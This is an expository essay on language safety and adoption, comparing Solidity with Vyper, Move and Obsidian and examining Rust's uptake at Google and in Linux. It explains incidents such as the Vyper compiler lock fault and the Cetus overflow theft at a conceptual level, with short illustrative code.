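The developers think familiarity was probably one of the big reasons for this success. Their surveys are consistent with that view but don't prove it. In Solidity's survey for 2021 (2022), 27% of respondents used JavaScript most and another 14.7% used TypeScript. In Solidity's survey for 2022 (2023), the combined share was 46%. Many contract developers evidently knew web technologies, as Wood had predicted. But nearly every contract needs a website through which people can use it, so these programmers might have been writing JavaScript whatever Solidity looked like. By early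 2026 the combined share had fallen to 29%, while 39% named Solidity as their main language.

Familiar notation did not guarantee success for Solidity's first rivals. Serpent, an earlier Ethereum language, looked like Python, which was already well known in 2014. The Solidity team says Serpent had significant shortcomings, and its ideas passed to a successor, Vyper. Solidity had another predecessor in Mutan, a contract language that Jeff Wilcke, another of Ethereum's founders, wrote in early 2014. Early Days of Ethereum's *mutan* dates its abandonment to just weeks before the network opened in 2015.

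Timing may still have mattered in a different way. Ethereum's own developers were promoting Solidity when the public arrived, so the first tutorials, libraries and token standards used it. Later developers found most of the code they needed already written. In Meyerovich and Rabkin's survey of programmers in general, libraries and existing code were among the strongest reasons for choosing a language. Contract developers have an additional reason to reuse code, because they can trust a library that has been used to hold other people's money for years without a theft more than a new one that only looks correct.

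The same is true of the auditors who check contracts. Projects commonly hire them before releasing a contract, and 12% of the survey's respondents were auditors or security experts. OpenZeppelin (2024), a company that also publishes widely used Solidity libraries, spent nearly four weeks auditing the core of Uniswap's fourth version and reported 24 issues, one of them critical. Solidity's flaws helped create this profession, which in turn makes Solidity harder to leave. A team that chooses a less common language may avoid some of those mistakes but will have fewer experts to find the rest.

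Solidity also benefits from its virtual machine, the EVM, which many newer blockchains copied so that they could run existing contracts. In the 2026 survey, 52% of respondents deployed to Ethereum itself, 40% to Base, 35% to Arbitrum and 30% to Polygon, all of which accept the same compiled code. This gives Solidity a large advantage over languages such as Move, which was designed for other machines, but none over Vyper, which also compiles to the EVM.

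The survey reached people mainly through Solidity's own channels, so it can't show how many developers prefer another language. Even so, 28% of respondents also used Rust for contracts, perhaps mostly on other blockchains, while 43% used no other contract language.

Solidity's familiar syntax probably mattered most at the beginning, when little else distinguished it from other new languages. The accumulated code, auditors and compatible blockchains better explain why it stayed ahead after its dangers were well known. Core Solidity may eventually make it possible to separate the effect of syntax from the effect of these accumulated advantages, since it will keep the machine and much of the notation, but programmers will have to give up part of their existing code.

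## Safer rivals to Solidity

After The DAO, several groups designed contract languages to prevent mistakes that Solidity allows. These languages are easier to compare than Ada and C, because contracts are short and mostly do similar things, such as holding and transferring assets. Vyper leaves out features that its designers considered risky. Move's type system prevents programs from copying assets or accidentally losing them. Obsidian, a research language, tracks who owns an asset and what state a contract is in.

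### Vyper leaves features out

Ethereum co-founder Vitalik Buterin conceived Vyper in November 2016, according to Blockworks' *From promise to niche*. It runs on the same virtual machine as Solidity but looks like Python. *TokenHook* (2021) presents the same token contract in both languages and lists what Vyper lacks: inheritance, modifiers, inline assembly (machine-level instructions inside a program) and overloading (several functions sharing a name).

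These omissions make a contract easier to check by reading it. A Solidity programmer can restrict a function to the contract's owner with a modifier:

```solidity
function close() public onlyOwner { ... }
```

The code for `onlyOwner` may be in another file, in a contract from which this one inherits. In Vyper the check has to be in the function or in something the function visibly calls:

```python
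@external
def close():
    assert msg.sender == self.owner
    ...
```

An auditor can see the rule at once, but Vyper does not require it, so a programmer who forgets the `assert` line leaves the function open to everyone, as Parity's programmers did. Vyper is safe by construction only against narrower errors. For example, a contract cannot use inline assembly to bypass the compiler's checks, and ordinary arithmetic fails on overflow.

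The Vyper version of the token took about 300 lines, compared with 500 in Solidity. *TokenHook* rates the two versions as equally secure, so careful programmers could achieve the same security in Solidity with more work. It also notes that most auditing tools supported only Solidity.

### Move makes assets a type

Facebook began developing Move in 2018 for Libra, a planned digital currency that never launched. The language's main idea is easiest to see in a token transfer. In Solidity, a token is a table of balances, and a transfer changes two numbers:

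```solidity
function transfer(address to, uint amount) public {
    balances[msg.sender] -= amount;
    balances[to] += amount;
}
```

If the programmer forgets the first line of the function's body, the recipient gets new tokens and the sender's balance doesn't change. If the programmer forgets the second line, the sender loses tokens that nobody receives. The compiler accepts both mistakes because it treats token balances as ordinary numbers.

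Blackshear, Cheng and colleagues, in *Move*, the white paper that introduced the language, give a payment script that looks like this with its names shortened:

```text
public main(payee: address, amount: u64) {
    let coin: Currency.Coin = Currency.withdraw_from_sender(copy(amount));
    Currency.deposit(copy(payee), move(coin));
}
```

The first step takes a coin out of the sender's account, and the second puts it into the recipient's. The script may copy the amount, which is an ordinary number, but the coin is a resource, which a program cannot copy and must move exactly once. Move rejects the script if the programmer changes `move(coin)` to `copy(coin)`, adds a line that deposits the same coin with someone else, or deletes the deposit line.

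Move still needs arithmetic on coins but confines it to the `Currency` module, because only the module that defines a coin can create one, destroy one or change its value. The programmer can still get the sums wrong inside that module. Blackshear and colleagues point out that if `deposit` added 1 to every payment, the type system would accept the code "without question".

A well-written Solidity token also keeps its balances in one contract, so Move's advantage is clearer when other contracts handle the token. *Resources* (Blackshear, Dill and colleagues, 2020) compares a simple bank in several languages. The Solidity bank needs a second table of what it owes each customer, and the programmer must keep that table correct too. The Move bank takes a coin and returns a `Credit`, which is also a resource. The `Credit` is a capability that a customer can give to someone else, who can then withdraw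 the money without any change to the bank's code.

The third language in the comparison, Scilla, forces a contract to update its records before it sends a payment, which prevents reentrancy. But a new notation can also introduce new errors. Scilla programmers sometimes wrote `emit` where they meant `send`, which destroyed the money.

The blockchain checks compiled Move code before accepting it, so an attacker cannot avoid the language's rules by bypassing the compiler and writing that code by hand. The original design also ruled out reentrancy. Every call had a fixed target, and a module could call only modules published before it, so a payment could not run an attacker's code that called back.

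### Obsidian tracks ownership and state

Obsidian resembles Java and runs on Hyperledger Fabric, a blockchain system for organisations. Each asset has exactly one owning reference, and the compiler reports an error if a program loses that reference. Types can also record an object's state, a feature called typestate. An auction, for example, can be `Open`, `BidsMade` or `Closed`, and the field that holds the highest bid exists only in the `BidsMade` state.

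Suppose a pharmacy accepts a prescription that allows a fixed number of refills. In the first version below, a patient can deposit the same prescription at several pharmacies and get all the refills at each:

```text
transaction deposit(Prescription@Shared p) returns int;
transaction deposit(Prescription@Owned >> Unowned p) returns int;
```

The second version requires the patient to own the prescription and transfers ownership to the pharmacy. Because the patient no longer owns the prescription, the compiler rejects code that deposits it at another pharmacy. In Solidity, the programmer would have to write a system to track refills across all the pharmacies.

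### The experiment with Obsidian and Solidity

Obsidian's designers tested it against Solidity by randomly assigning ten people to each language (Coblenz, Aldrich and colleagues, 2020, *Can Advanced Type Systems Be Usable?*). They recruited at their university, but 18 of the 20 participants had worked as programmers, and all had to answer basic questions about Java to take part. Each session lasted up to four hours, including about an hour and a half of training. The Solidity group also learned about ownership and could record it in comments, so that any difference between the groups would come more from the language than from the training.

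In the first task, participants had 30 minutes to complete the code for an auction that refunds the previous bidder when a higher bid arrives. In the second, they had 35 minutes to fix the prescription problem. In the third, they had to write most of a casino's betting system.

| Task and result | Solidity | Obsidian |
|---|---|---|
| Auction: correct | 2 of 10 | 7 of 10 |
| Auction: lost an asset | 7 of 10 | 0 of 10 |
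| Auction: average time for those who finished | 12 minutes | 12 minutes |
| Prescription: correct | 2 of 10 | 7 of 10 |
| Prescription: average time for correct solutions | 20 minutes | 22 minutes |
| Casino: lost or wrongly created tokens | 4 of 8 | 4 of 4 |
| Casino: average time for those who finished | 37 minutes | 64 minutes |

In the auction task, four Solidity participants wrote `=` where they needed `+=`, so a new refund erased an earlier one. Three forgot to refund the old bid. The Obsidian compiler caught lost assets in two participants' programs, and both participants fixed the errors. It did not stop another participant from refunding the wrong bidder, because the money still had an owner.

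In the casino task, by contrast, all four Obsidian participants who finished used `disown`, the language's escape hatch for discarding an asset, to throw away tokens that the casino should have kept or paid out. One wrote in a comment that the code "just throws the bettor's money away and hopes they find it eventually". The tutorial had warned against this use. Some participants may have wanted to get rid of compiler errors, and others may not have understood what an asset was.

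With ten people in each group, the experiment can detect only large effects. Chance is unlikely to explain the difference in lost assets in the auction. The difference in correct solutions is less certain. Coblenz and colleagues compared only those who finished, and a difference as large as the one they found would arise by chance about 1.5% of the time if the languages were equally good. If people who ran out of time count as failures, the same test gives about 7%. The casino results are weaker still, because only the fastest Obsidian participants reached that task.

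Some features of the experiment also favoured Obsidian. Participants could compile their programs but not run them, so the Solidity group could not find mistakes by testing. Solidity participants had to store refunds for later collection, a standard defence against reentrancy, while Obsidian participants could return the money directly. In the prescription task, the instructions led half of the Solidity group to try ownership, which their compiler does not check. But the Solidity group had more programming experience, with a median of 9.2 years against 5.0.

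The auction task shows that newcomers often lose assets in Solidity and that a compiler can catch this mistake for programmers who have had a short lesson in its language. The extra time on the casino task plausibly came from learning a strict language, but the study was too short to show whether that time shrinks with practice. The study also could not show whether experienced programmers would use `disown` more carefully.

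### How many people use them

Solidity and Vyper dominate the 1,000 Ethereum contracts that hold the most value, according to Lehmann's *Programming Languages Securing Ethereum's Value* (2026). Most of Vyper's share is in a few contracts belonging to Curve, an exchange that also funds the language. In a grant report, Vyper's developers put the value in Vyper contracts at more than $4 billion across several blockchains. These totals partly reflect old choices of language, since a successful contract can hold money for years after it was written. Peterson's *Vyper turns 8* describes a steady decline in Vyper's share over several years.

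Move's best-known blockchains are Sui and Aptos. CoinGecko's *Top Blockchains by Total Value Locked (TVL)* counted $72.7 billion locked on all blockchains in mid-2026, 54% of it on Ethereum. Neither Sui nor Aptos was in the top five, so each held less than fifth-placed Base, which had $4.4 billion. Trackers' totals vary widely, but Move's blockchains are clearly far behind Ethereum.

Developer counts show the same pattern. Syndica's *Deep Dive* (2026) finds that Solana, where programmers mostly use Rust, has 60% of the weekly active developers on blockchains that do not use Ethereum's virtual machine. Sui is a distant third. BlockEden.xyz (2026) puts Solana's weekly developers at 942. The two sources count differently, but together they suggest that Sui has roughly 300 at most. Aptos lost 60% of its developers in the year to early 2026, while Ethereum lost 34% and Solana 40%.

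Obsidian's designers tested it on realistic applications, but it does not seem to have spread beyond research or gained many users.

Move's adoption is poor evidence that programmers prefer its design, because developers have to use it to write contracts for Sui or Aptos. Syndica's figures suggest that many people choose a blockchain before a language. About 87% of Solana's developers and 86% of Ethereum's began their blockchain work on that blockchain, usually after years of other programming. Vyper is a better test, since Ethereum developers can use either it or Solidity for the same job. Most use Solidity, even though Vyper's notation is familiar to Python programmers. Vyper's smaller selection of tools and libraries may be part of the reason.

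Move's design probably did matter to the people who built the blockchains. Cheng and Blackshear, two of the language's designers, later co-founded the company behind Sui. In The Move Book's *Foreword*, Blackshear writes that a new language must be ten times better than its rivals in some relevant way to have a chance, but that the quality of its community matters even more. Move gained most of its programmers because they were required to use it, as Ada did, though blockchain developers can avoid the requirement by choosing another platform.

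### The Vyper compiler fault

Vyper has a built-in defence against reentrancy. A programmer labels functions with `@nonreentrant("lock")`, and while one of them is running, no function with the same label should start. On 30 July 2023, attackers drained several Curve pools whose source code used these labels correctly.

The compiler had given each function its own lock. OtterSec's *Vyper hack timeline* shows compiled code in which the function for adding money to a pool checks storage slot 0, while the function for removing money checks slot 2. Both should have used the same slot. An attacker receiving a withdrawal could therefore re-enter the pool through the function for adding money, whose lock was still open.

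The Vyper team's post-mortem traces the fault to a reorganisation of the compiler in 2021. A user upgrading the code of Yearn, an investment service, noticed that reentrancy tests failed with version 0.2.14. The developers withdrew that version, but their repair in 0.2.15 removed the check that gave functions with the same label one shared lock. Nobody noticed the new fault because Vyper's own tests did not cover an attack that went from one function to another.

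Four months later, a developer noticed the compiler reserving more storage than it needed and called this "an optimization bug". The fix in version 0.3.1 restored the shared lock, and the team added the missing test. But the developers did not realise that contracts already on the blockchain were in danger, and did not warn their owners. Attackers exploited the fault about 20 months later. They took an estimated $70 million (Behnke, 2023, *Explained*), though well-meaning hackers reduced final losses to about $52 million.

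An auditor who read only the Vyper source could not have found this error. Contracts that updated their records before sending money were safe even without a working lock. But some contracts cannot update their records first, because they need the result of an outside call to finish their own work.

### The Cetus theft

Cetus was the largest exchange on Sui when an attacker drained about $223 million from it on 22 May 2025. Move, Sui's contract language, stops a program if an addition or multiplication overflows, but a left shift, which multiplies a number by a power of two, discards the digits that do not fit. The security company BlockSec explains that programmers therefore have to check shifts themselves. Cetus used an open-source library whose check was wrong.

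The code shifted 256-bit numbers left by 64 bits, which is safe only for numbers below 2¹⁹². According to ChainCatcher, the faulty check rejected only numbers above 2²⁵⁶ − 2¹⁹², so it let through almost every number that was too large. In an 8-bit version of the mistake, numbers go up to 255 and shifting left by 2 bits multiplies them by 4, so the largest safe number is 63. The equivalent check would allow anything up to 192, so 65 would pass and the result would be 4 instead of 260.

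At Cetus, this error made an enormous deposit appear to cost one unit of a token. The attacker paid that unit and then withdrew real money against the deposit. Blockworks' *Sui shares details on $220M Cetus exploit, vows to step up security* reports that about $162 million was still frozen four days later.

The attacker did not copy any coins, and none disappeared, so Move's guarantee held. The exchange paid out the coins because of an error in its own arithmetic, a kind of mistake that the white paper had said the type system could not catch.

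### Fewer users and fewer eyes

Both failures were in code that many contracts shared. When a language has few users, fewer people might find such faults, and the Vyper case is some direct evidence of this. Yearn's tests exposed the fault in version 0.2.14 soon after its release, and more projects with their own tests might have exposed the next fault. Several other projects on Sui relied on the same library as Cetus, according to OpenZeppelin, but none caught the error in time. OpenZeppelin, which has an interest in promoting shared libraries, released its own for Sui only after the theft.

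Solidity's record shows that popularity is not enough to make contracts safe. The DAO and Parity's wallets both had many users, yet both had serious flaws. Most large thefts from Solidity contracts exploited the logic of a particular application. That logic is new each time, so it benefits little from the number of people using the language.

Comparing compilers is fairer, because every contract in a language depends on its compiler. None of the major Solidity thefts from The DAO to GMX came from a compiler fault. Solidity's compiler has had bugs, and 13% of respondents to Solidity's latest survey reported recurring problems with its optimizer, though these may not be security faults. Solidity's larger user base probably helps find dangerous bugs sooner, but an undiscovered bug could also affect far more money. Vyper's compiler has had one disaster, which is too little evidence to compare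 failure rates.

Money may matter as much as the number of users. Solidity's developers belong to an organisation of about 25 people, while Vyper's team used a $50,000 grant to help pay four core contributors and fund security audits. CertiK, another security company, noted after the 2023 attack that Vyper had no programme to reward people who reported bugs. Vyper's team then announced rewards for bugs found in any version of the compiler, and outside reviews of the old versions whose contracts still held large sums.

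## Rust, and how a strict compiler gained users

Few Solidity users have switched to its safer rivals, but Rust has made more headway against C and C++, the languages behind most operating systems and browsers. Mozilla, which makes the Firefox browser, developed Rust as a safer alternative. Rust's compiler rejects a lot of code that a C++ programmer would consider normal, but Google now adds about as much new Rust as C++ to Android, its phone operating system. Google has also published measurements of the results.

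### Ownership and borrowing

A C++ compiler accepts this code:

```cpp
std::vector<int> v = {10, 20, 30};
int& first = v[0];
v.push_back(40);
std::cout << first;
```

`v` is a list that can grow, and `first` refers to the memory that holds its first number. When the third line adds a fourth number, the list usually has no room for it, so the program copies the list to a larger block of memory and frees the old block. `first` still refers to the old block, so the last line reads freed memory, an error called use-after-free. The program may print 10, print nonsense or crash. An attacker can sometimes use such an error to take control of software that handles untrusted data.

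Most languages avoid this with a garbage collector, which runs alongside the program and frees memory only when nothing refers to it any more. Garbage collectors cost time and memory, so they suit operating systems and small devices poorly. Rust has no garbage collector and makes its checks at compile time. The same code in Rust looks much like the C++ version:

```rust
let mut v = vec![10, 20, 30];
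let first = &v[0];
v.push(40);
println!("{first}");
```

The compiler rejects the third line with the message "cannot borrow `v` as mutable because it is also borrowed as immutable". Every value in Rust has one owner, and Rust frees the value when its owner goes out of scope. Other code can borrow the value through references. At any moment, a value can have either several read-only references or one that can change it, and no reference may outlast the value. Here `first` is a read-only reference that lasts until its final use in the fourth line, but `push` needs one that can change the list. If the programmer prints the number before adding the new one, the borrow ends before `push` runs and the code compiles.

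Ownership can also move. If `x` owns a piece of text and the programmer writes `let y = x;`, `y` becomes the owner and the compiler rejects any later use of `x`. Python and C++ programmers would expect both names to keep working.

These rules also reject some harmless programs. *Learning and Programming Challenges of Rust*, by Zhu, Zhang and colleagues, describes a function that takes two references, one for changing a value and one for reading another. A programmer cannot pass it the first two elements of an array by position, although the elements don't overlap, because the compiler treats a borrow of one element as a borrow of the whole array. The compiler accepts the call if the two values are fields of a tuple, a fixed group of values. The rules also make it hard to write a doubly linked list, in which each item points to both its neighbours. Programmers normally take such structures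 from a library that uses Rust's escape hatch internally.

### Unsafe code behind a safe interface

An `unsafe` block allows five kinds of operation that the compiler cannot check, such as following a raw pointer or calling a function marked as unsafe. The other checks stay on inside the block. Programmers usually put the block inside a function that others can call safely:

```rust
fn first(list: &[i32]) -> Option<i32> {
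    if list.is_empty() {
        return None;
    }
    // The list is not empty, so element 0 exists.
    Some(unsafe { *list.get_unchecked(0) })
}
```

`get_unchecked` reads an element without checking that it exists. `first` checks this beforehand, so its callers don't need an `unsafe` block. Programmers call such a function sound, meaning that no caller written only in safe Rust can use it to break memory safety. But if someone deletes the `if` statement, the code still compiles, and calling `first` on an empty list reads memory outside the list.

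In *Benefits and Drawbacks of Adopting a Secure Programming Language*, Fulton, Chan and colleagues (2021) interviewed 16 professionals, mostly senior developers, and surveyed 178 members of online Rust forums. Of the survey respondents, 72% had used unsafe blocks, most often to call code in other languages. Only 28% said their employers had a procedure for reviewing such blocks. *Rethinking Toolchain Design for Rust* cites a 2020 study by Qin and colleagues in which every Rust memory bug involved unsafe code, though many also involved safe code. A reviewer may therefore have to read the code around an unsafe block as well as the block itself.

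### What Rust kept familiar

Rust uses braces and many of C's keywords, and its compiler infers the types of most local variables. Rust programs run about as fast as C programs. Rust and C code can call each other's functions, so a team can replace one part of a C system and keep the rest. In a survey by Fulton and colleagues, 70% of respondents who had connected Rust to C found it easy, compared with 43% of those who had connected it to C++.

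Similar notation did not make it easier to rewrite old programs. Of those who had moved code from Python to Rust, 70% found it easy, compared with 54% for C and 52% for C++. One interviewee explained that C++ programs organise their data around values that many parts of the code can change, which Rust forbids. The groups had only 33 to 44 people, and the Python programs may have been simpler. Still, the answers fit the distinction between surface and semantic familiarity, since a C++ programmer can read much of a Rust program immediately but may still have to redesign their own program to move it to Rust.

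### What learners and employers pay

Fulton and colleagues found that 59% of respondents considered Rust harder to learn than other languages. When asked how long they had needed before they could write programs that compiled without frequent use of `unsafe`, 27% said less than a week, 41% said between a week and a month, and 25% said between one and six months. Six people said they still could not do it. One interviewee described "a near-vertical learning curve".

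Zhu and colleagues looked for the causes in 100 questions that programmers had posted on Stack Overflow after breaking a safety rule. They then asked 101 programmers to mark the code at fault in short programs. Average scores per program ranged from 0.39 to 0.75 out of 1. Lifetimes, which determine how long a reference remains valid, caused more trouble than ownership. Only 10% of participants said they always understood compiler messages about lifetimes, compared with 40% for ownership.

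Some of this difficulty came from the compiler's error messages. In the array example, the message reported the conflicting borrows but omitted that an array's elements count as borrowed together. When Zhu and colleagues added this, participants explained the error significantly better. Better messages could therefore make Rust easier without weakening any of its rules.

The difficulty of borrowing seems to fade with practice. *What we heard about Rust's challenges* (Huey, 2026) draws on about 70 interviews by a team from the Rust project. Nearly every beginner struggled with borrowing, but experts had mostly stopped complaining about it. They still complained about slow compilation, about code that waits for several tasks at once, and about choosing or finding libraries. People who gave up on Rust never became experts, so comparing beginners with experts makes learning look more successful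 than it is. The post is also a personal commentary without quotations. Huey wrote it after retracting a version first drafted by a language model.

Companies had their own reservations. In the survey by Fulton and colleagues, 41% of respondents had met resistance from colleagues or managers. They reported these concerns at their employers:

| Concern | Share of respondents |
|---|---|
| Nobody knew Rust well | 69% |
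| Rust was hard to learn | 50% |
| The company did not want another language | 46% |
| Rust developers would be hard to hire | 42% |
| There was no time before a deadline | 38% |
| Rust and its tools might not last | 29% |
| Rust would not work well with existing code | 27% |

Most of these objections would apply to any new language, even one with a lax compiler. Only the difficulty of learning Rust comes mainly from its strictness, and that difficulty probably adds to the worry about hiring.

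In return, 89% of respondents said they spent less time debugging Rust code than code in another language they knew well. The figure was 87% among those with less than a year of Rust experience, so newcomers can notice this benefit early, as the students in Software AG's functional programming course did. Fewer respondents (45%) thought Rust shortened a project overall. The respondents all belonged to Rust forums, which probably had few members who had tried the language and given it up.

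### More admired than used

According to Zhu and colleagues, Rust had been the most loved language in Stack Overflow's annual survey every year since 2016. The ranking is based on the share of a language's users who want to keep using it, so a language with a small but enthusiastic user base can come first.

Rust ranks lower by use. Stack Overflow's *The results of the 2026 Developer Survey are here!* (2026) places it 12th, up from the year before, while JavaScript leads with 62% of respondents. Slashdot's *Rust Leaves Top 10 in TIOBE Index, Making Room for Go* (2026) reports that Rust fell out of the top ten in November in the TIOBE index, which is based on search results. One month's movement in such an index means little, but neither source puts Rust near the most popular languages.

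Much Rust use is still unpaid. A survey by the toolmaker JetBrains (2026) found that 65% of Rust users wrote it for hobbies or side projects and 52% were still learning it. Only 26% used it in professional projects, up from 16% in an earlier JetBrains survey. Many of these people come to Rust out of curiosity and can try it on their own, but using it at work also takes an employer's consent. Curiosity was a main reason for learning Rust for 90% of respondents in a survey by Fulton and colleagues, and when Crichton and Krishnamurthi added quizzes to a Rust textbook in 2022, more than 62,000 readers answered questions within about a year.

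Professional demand for Rust appears to be growing. Rust Blog's *2025 State of Rust Survey Results* (2026), based on 7,156 responses, reports that more organisations are looking for Rust developers. The number of Rust developers understates the language's importance, since a small team can write code that runs on billions of phones.

### Google's measurements on Android

Google introduced Rust into Android as an alternative to C and C++ for new system code, and left most of the old code in place. *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025), a post on Google's security blog, reports that by November 2025 Android contained about 5 million lines of Rust, and Google's own developers were adding slightly more Rust than C++.

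| Measure | Rust | C++, or C and C++ in the last row |
|---|---|---|
| Revisions before approval, for changes of similar size | About 20% fewer | Baseline |
| Time in code review | About 25% less | Baseline |
| Rollbacks of medium and large changes | About a quarter of the rate | Baseline |
| Memory-safety vulnerabilities per million lines | 0.2 | About 1,000 |

A rollback undoes a change that developers have already added, usually because it broke something. Google adopted Rust for its security, and Vander Stoep calls its effect on development speed the biggest surprise.

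Memory-safety flaws also fell below 20% of all Android vulnerabilities for the first time in 2025. In 2019 they made up roughly 75%, according to SiliconANGLE. If the number of other vulnerabilities had stayed the same, this would mean that memory-safety flaws fell by roughly 90%. But the share could also fall because researchers found more flaws of other kinds. The figure covers all of Android, including code in Java and Kotlin, so the decline cannot be attributed entirely to Rust.

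### How well the comparison holds up

The rate of 0.2 flaws per million lines is uncertain because it is based on a single flaw in 5 million lines. If such flaws occur independently, the 95% confidence interval for the expected number in that much code extends up to about 5.6, or 1.1 per million lines. Even that rate is about 900 times lower than the rate for C and C++.

The age of the code is a bigger problem. People have searched Android's C and C++ code for flaws for many years, while most of the Rust dates from 2023 or later. Vander Stoep calls the rate for C and C++ "historical" without giving the period, and programmers may write safer C++ today. Suppose researchers have found only a tenth of the flaws in the Rust code, and new C++ has only a tenth of the historical rate. The rates would then be 2 flaws per million lines for Rust and 100 for C++, a factor of 50. Google's factor of over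 1,000 is therefore uncertain, but only very large errors would eliminate the difference.

The figures on rollbacks and review are weaker evidence. A team that writes a new component in Rust can design it from scratch, while a change in C++ often alters old code that other parts depend on, and is more likely to break something. Google's analysts grouped changes by size and counted only those by Android's own developers, many of whom write both languages. But they did not assign languages at random, and Vander Stoep gives no separate results for new components or for the same developer working in both languages. Verdix's comparison of C and Ada had the same weakness, because Verdix's oldest code was in C.

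Better programmers might also have volunteered for Rust first. In that case, the rollback rate should have risen as Rust spread to other teams, but it kept falling. Vander Stoep does suspect, though, that growing experience with Rust explains much of the improvement in review times between 2023 and 2024. Review was faster mainly for large changes, with little difference for small ones. Google also gives no absolute rollback rates, so outsiders cannot tell how much work the lower rate saves. The data make it unlikely that Rust slowed these teams down, as many employers had feared, but don't establish that the language itself made review 25% faster.

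### The near miss

The figure of 0.2 reflects one flaw, in CrabbyAVIF, a Rust library for reading images. Unsafe code in the library could run past the end of a block of memory. Google fixed the flaw before any public release and gave it the identifier CVE-2025-48530 so that the fix would get priority.

An attacker could not have exploited the overflow on a phone with Scudo, Android's standard memory allocator, which surrounds large blocks with pages that no program may touch. The overflow hit one of these pages and crashed the program instead of silently damaging other data. The crash report did not show that an overflow was the cause, which delayed the response, and Google has since corrected this. Google's defence therefore depended partly on the allocator as well as on Rust, and other phone makers are not yet required to use Scudo.

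About 4% of Android's Rust code, some 200,000 lines, is in unsafe blocks. If those lines had as many memory-safety vulnerabilities per line as Google's historical C and C++ code, they would contain about 200, but Google had found one. Vander Stoep suggests that unsafe Rust has fewer vulnerabilities because most of Rust's checks still apply, each block is small enough to reason about, and reviewers pay extra attention to unsafe code.

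### What AI agents found in 2026

Rust programs often use C libraries through a binding, a Rust library that wraps C functions in a safe interface. Its authors have to translate the C library's rules about memory into Rust's types. Momeu and Sen (2026), in *Agentic Discovery of Soundness Bugs in Safe Rust Bindings*, used AI agents to look for places where that translation had gone wrong. One was in `ssh2`, a library for secure connections:

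```rust
let first = session.auth_methods("root").unwrap();
let second = session.auth_methods("root").unwrap();
println!("{first}");
```

The first call returns text in a buffer belonging to the C library. The second call frees that buffer, so the last line reads freed memory, as in the C++ example with the list. The programmer has written no unsafe code, and the compiler accepts the program because the binding declares that `auth_methods` only reads the session. If the binding declared that each call changes the session, the compiler would reject the second call while `first` was still in use.

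The agents read the Rust and C code together, wrote programs that broke the rules, and ran most of them under tools that detect memory errors. In 19 widely used Rust packages, they found 213 bugs that cause undefined behaviour, meaning the language guarantees nothing about what the program does. A caller could reach 191 of these without writing any unsafe code. The median audit cost $42. Momeu and Sen reported 78 of the bugs to the packages' maintainers, who have fixed 24 and rejected none. A separate audit of the Rust code in the Linux kernel found 11 more such bugs.

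These numbers are compatible with Google's. Google counted vulnerabilities in its own products, while Momeu and Sen counted interfaces that some program could misuse, and they chose packages that mostly wrap C or C++ code. To exploit most of the bugs, an attacker would need an application that uses the interface in a particular way. Some applications do, including gitui, a program for managing versions of code. The agents found that it could read outside its memory when it opened a maliciously altered file.

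A programmer who never writes `unsafe` still depends on whoever wrote each binding the program uses. The audits therefore weaken the common understanding that Rust's guarantee leaves such a programmer with nothing to worry about. Some repairs also inconvenience users. The maintainers of `git2` fixed a bug by forbidding programs to move one kind of object between threads, which are parts of a program that run at the same time, and labelled this a breaking change. AI agents make similar mistakes when they write bindings. In *Crustify*, a related project by Momeu, Arvinte and colleagues (2026), reviewing agents fixed 21 defects in two generated bindings. These defects let Rust code cause undefined behaviour.

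Other flaws have nothing to do with memory. Another AI-assisted search of Rust projects, published on Openwall (2026), found logic errors and programs that crash or slow down severely on hostile input. According to Openwall, Rust removes "many memory-safety bugs, but not security bugs".

### Sponsors, Linux and governments

Rust has had wealthy backers. Mozilla paid for much of its early development, and in 2021 Google, Microsoft, Amazon's cloud division, Huawei and Mozilla founded the Rust Foundation. The foundation supports contributors and the security of Rust's libraries, according to its *2025 Annual Report* (2026). Slashdot's *The Rust Ecosystem Gets an AI Security Engineer in Residence* reports that in 2026 the foundation gained funding for a full-time engineer to review Rust and its most important packages with the help of AI. Some maintainers still lack funding, and the Rust Blog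 asks companies to support those who might otherwise leave after long periods of unpaid work.

The Linux kernel is written mostly in C, and its developers accepted Rust as an experiment in 2022. Some maintainers of C code objected that a second language would make the kernel harder to maintain, and that they might have to repair Rust code whenever they changed their own. The dispute became bitter, and several supporters of Rust resigned. In early 2025, when a maintainer tried to block a Rust interface to a part of the kernel written in C, the project's leader, Linus Torvalds, replied that maintainers could ignore Rust but could not veto code outside their own area. That December the kernel's maintainers declared Rust "no longer experimental", according to Dev Newsletter's *State of Rust 2026* (2026). Android's first production driver in Rust runs on version 6.12 of the kernel.

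The US National Security Agency recommended memory-safe languages in November 2022, and the White House did so in February 2024. The FBI and the US cybersecurity agency CISA then urged makers of software for critical infrastructure to publish plans by 1 January 2026 for dealing with memory-unsafe code. This guidance was voluntary, unlike the Defense Department's order to use Ada, and it did not single out Rust, since Java, C# and Go are memory safe too. Miller (2024) argued in *Investing in Rust* for more help from public policy because the adoption of safer languages had stalled in some fields.

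Stack Overflow raises the possibility that the White House document helped Rust rise in its 2026 ranking, but has no evidence that it did. The US guidance came too late to explain why the first large adopters chose Rust. Microsoft's security team was already recommending the language in 2019, and Google was using it in Android before the first US guidance appeared.

### What safety won

People who use Rust at work name safety and speed about equally often. In a 2021 community survey reported in Slashdot's *Programming in Rust is Fun* (2022), 96% said they used it to write relatively correct software, 92% for performance and 89% for security. Fulton and colleagues found that 90% of respondents listed memory safety among Rust's benefits and 87% listed performance. Safety ranked tenth in Meyerovich and Rabkin's survey of programmers in general, but these results conflict less than they seem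 to, because the Rust users had already chosen the language.

Rust's main advantage is for programmers who need both memory safety and speed, such as the makers of operating systems and browsers. Programmers who can accept a garbage collector have had memory safety for decades in Java and Python, and more recently in Go, which is easier to learn than Rust. Those who want only speed can stay with C++. These alternatives help explain why Rust's share of all programmers remains modest.

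Tools made Rust easier to adopt. In the survey by Fulton and colleagues, 92% of respondents rated Rust's error messages better than those of the language they knew best, and 83% liked Rust's packages. Cargo, the program that builds Rust code and downloads its libraries, was the most admired infrastructure tool in a Stack Overflow survey, where 71% of its users wanted to keep using it. Ada lacked such tools in its early years, but the comparison is imperfect because Ada's checks do not stop a program from freeing memory that other code still uses.

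The effects of sponsorship and safety on Rust's adoption are hard to separate, because some sponsors turned to Rust after recording security flaws in their own software. Microsoft's *Why Rust for safe systems programming* (2019) estimated that Rust would most likely have prevented the 70% of the company's security issues that came from memory errors. Microsoft and Google both had security teams that counted such flaws across the work of thousands of programmers, and both companies could pay for the training and libraries needed to switch.

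## Adding safety to a language people already use

A company that adopts Rust still has its old code. Google (2025) estimated that it had around a billion lines of C++. It writes new code in memory-safe languages where it can and adds checks to its existing C++.

Adding checks to a language or removing its riskier features lets programmers keep most of what they know. SPARK does this for Ada, and Solidity's developers did it when they made arithmetic fail on overflow. Some engineers now do the same for AI agents by letting them write only a restricted form of Python. The most widely used example is TypeScript, which adds types to JavaScript.

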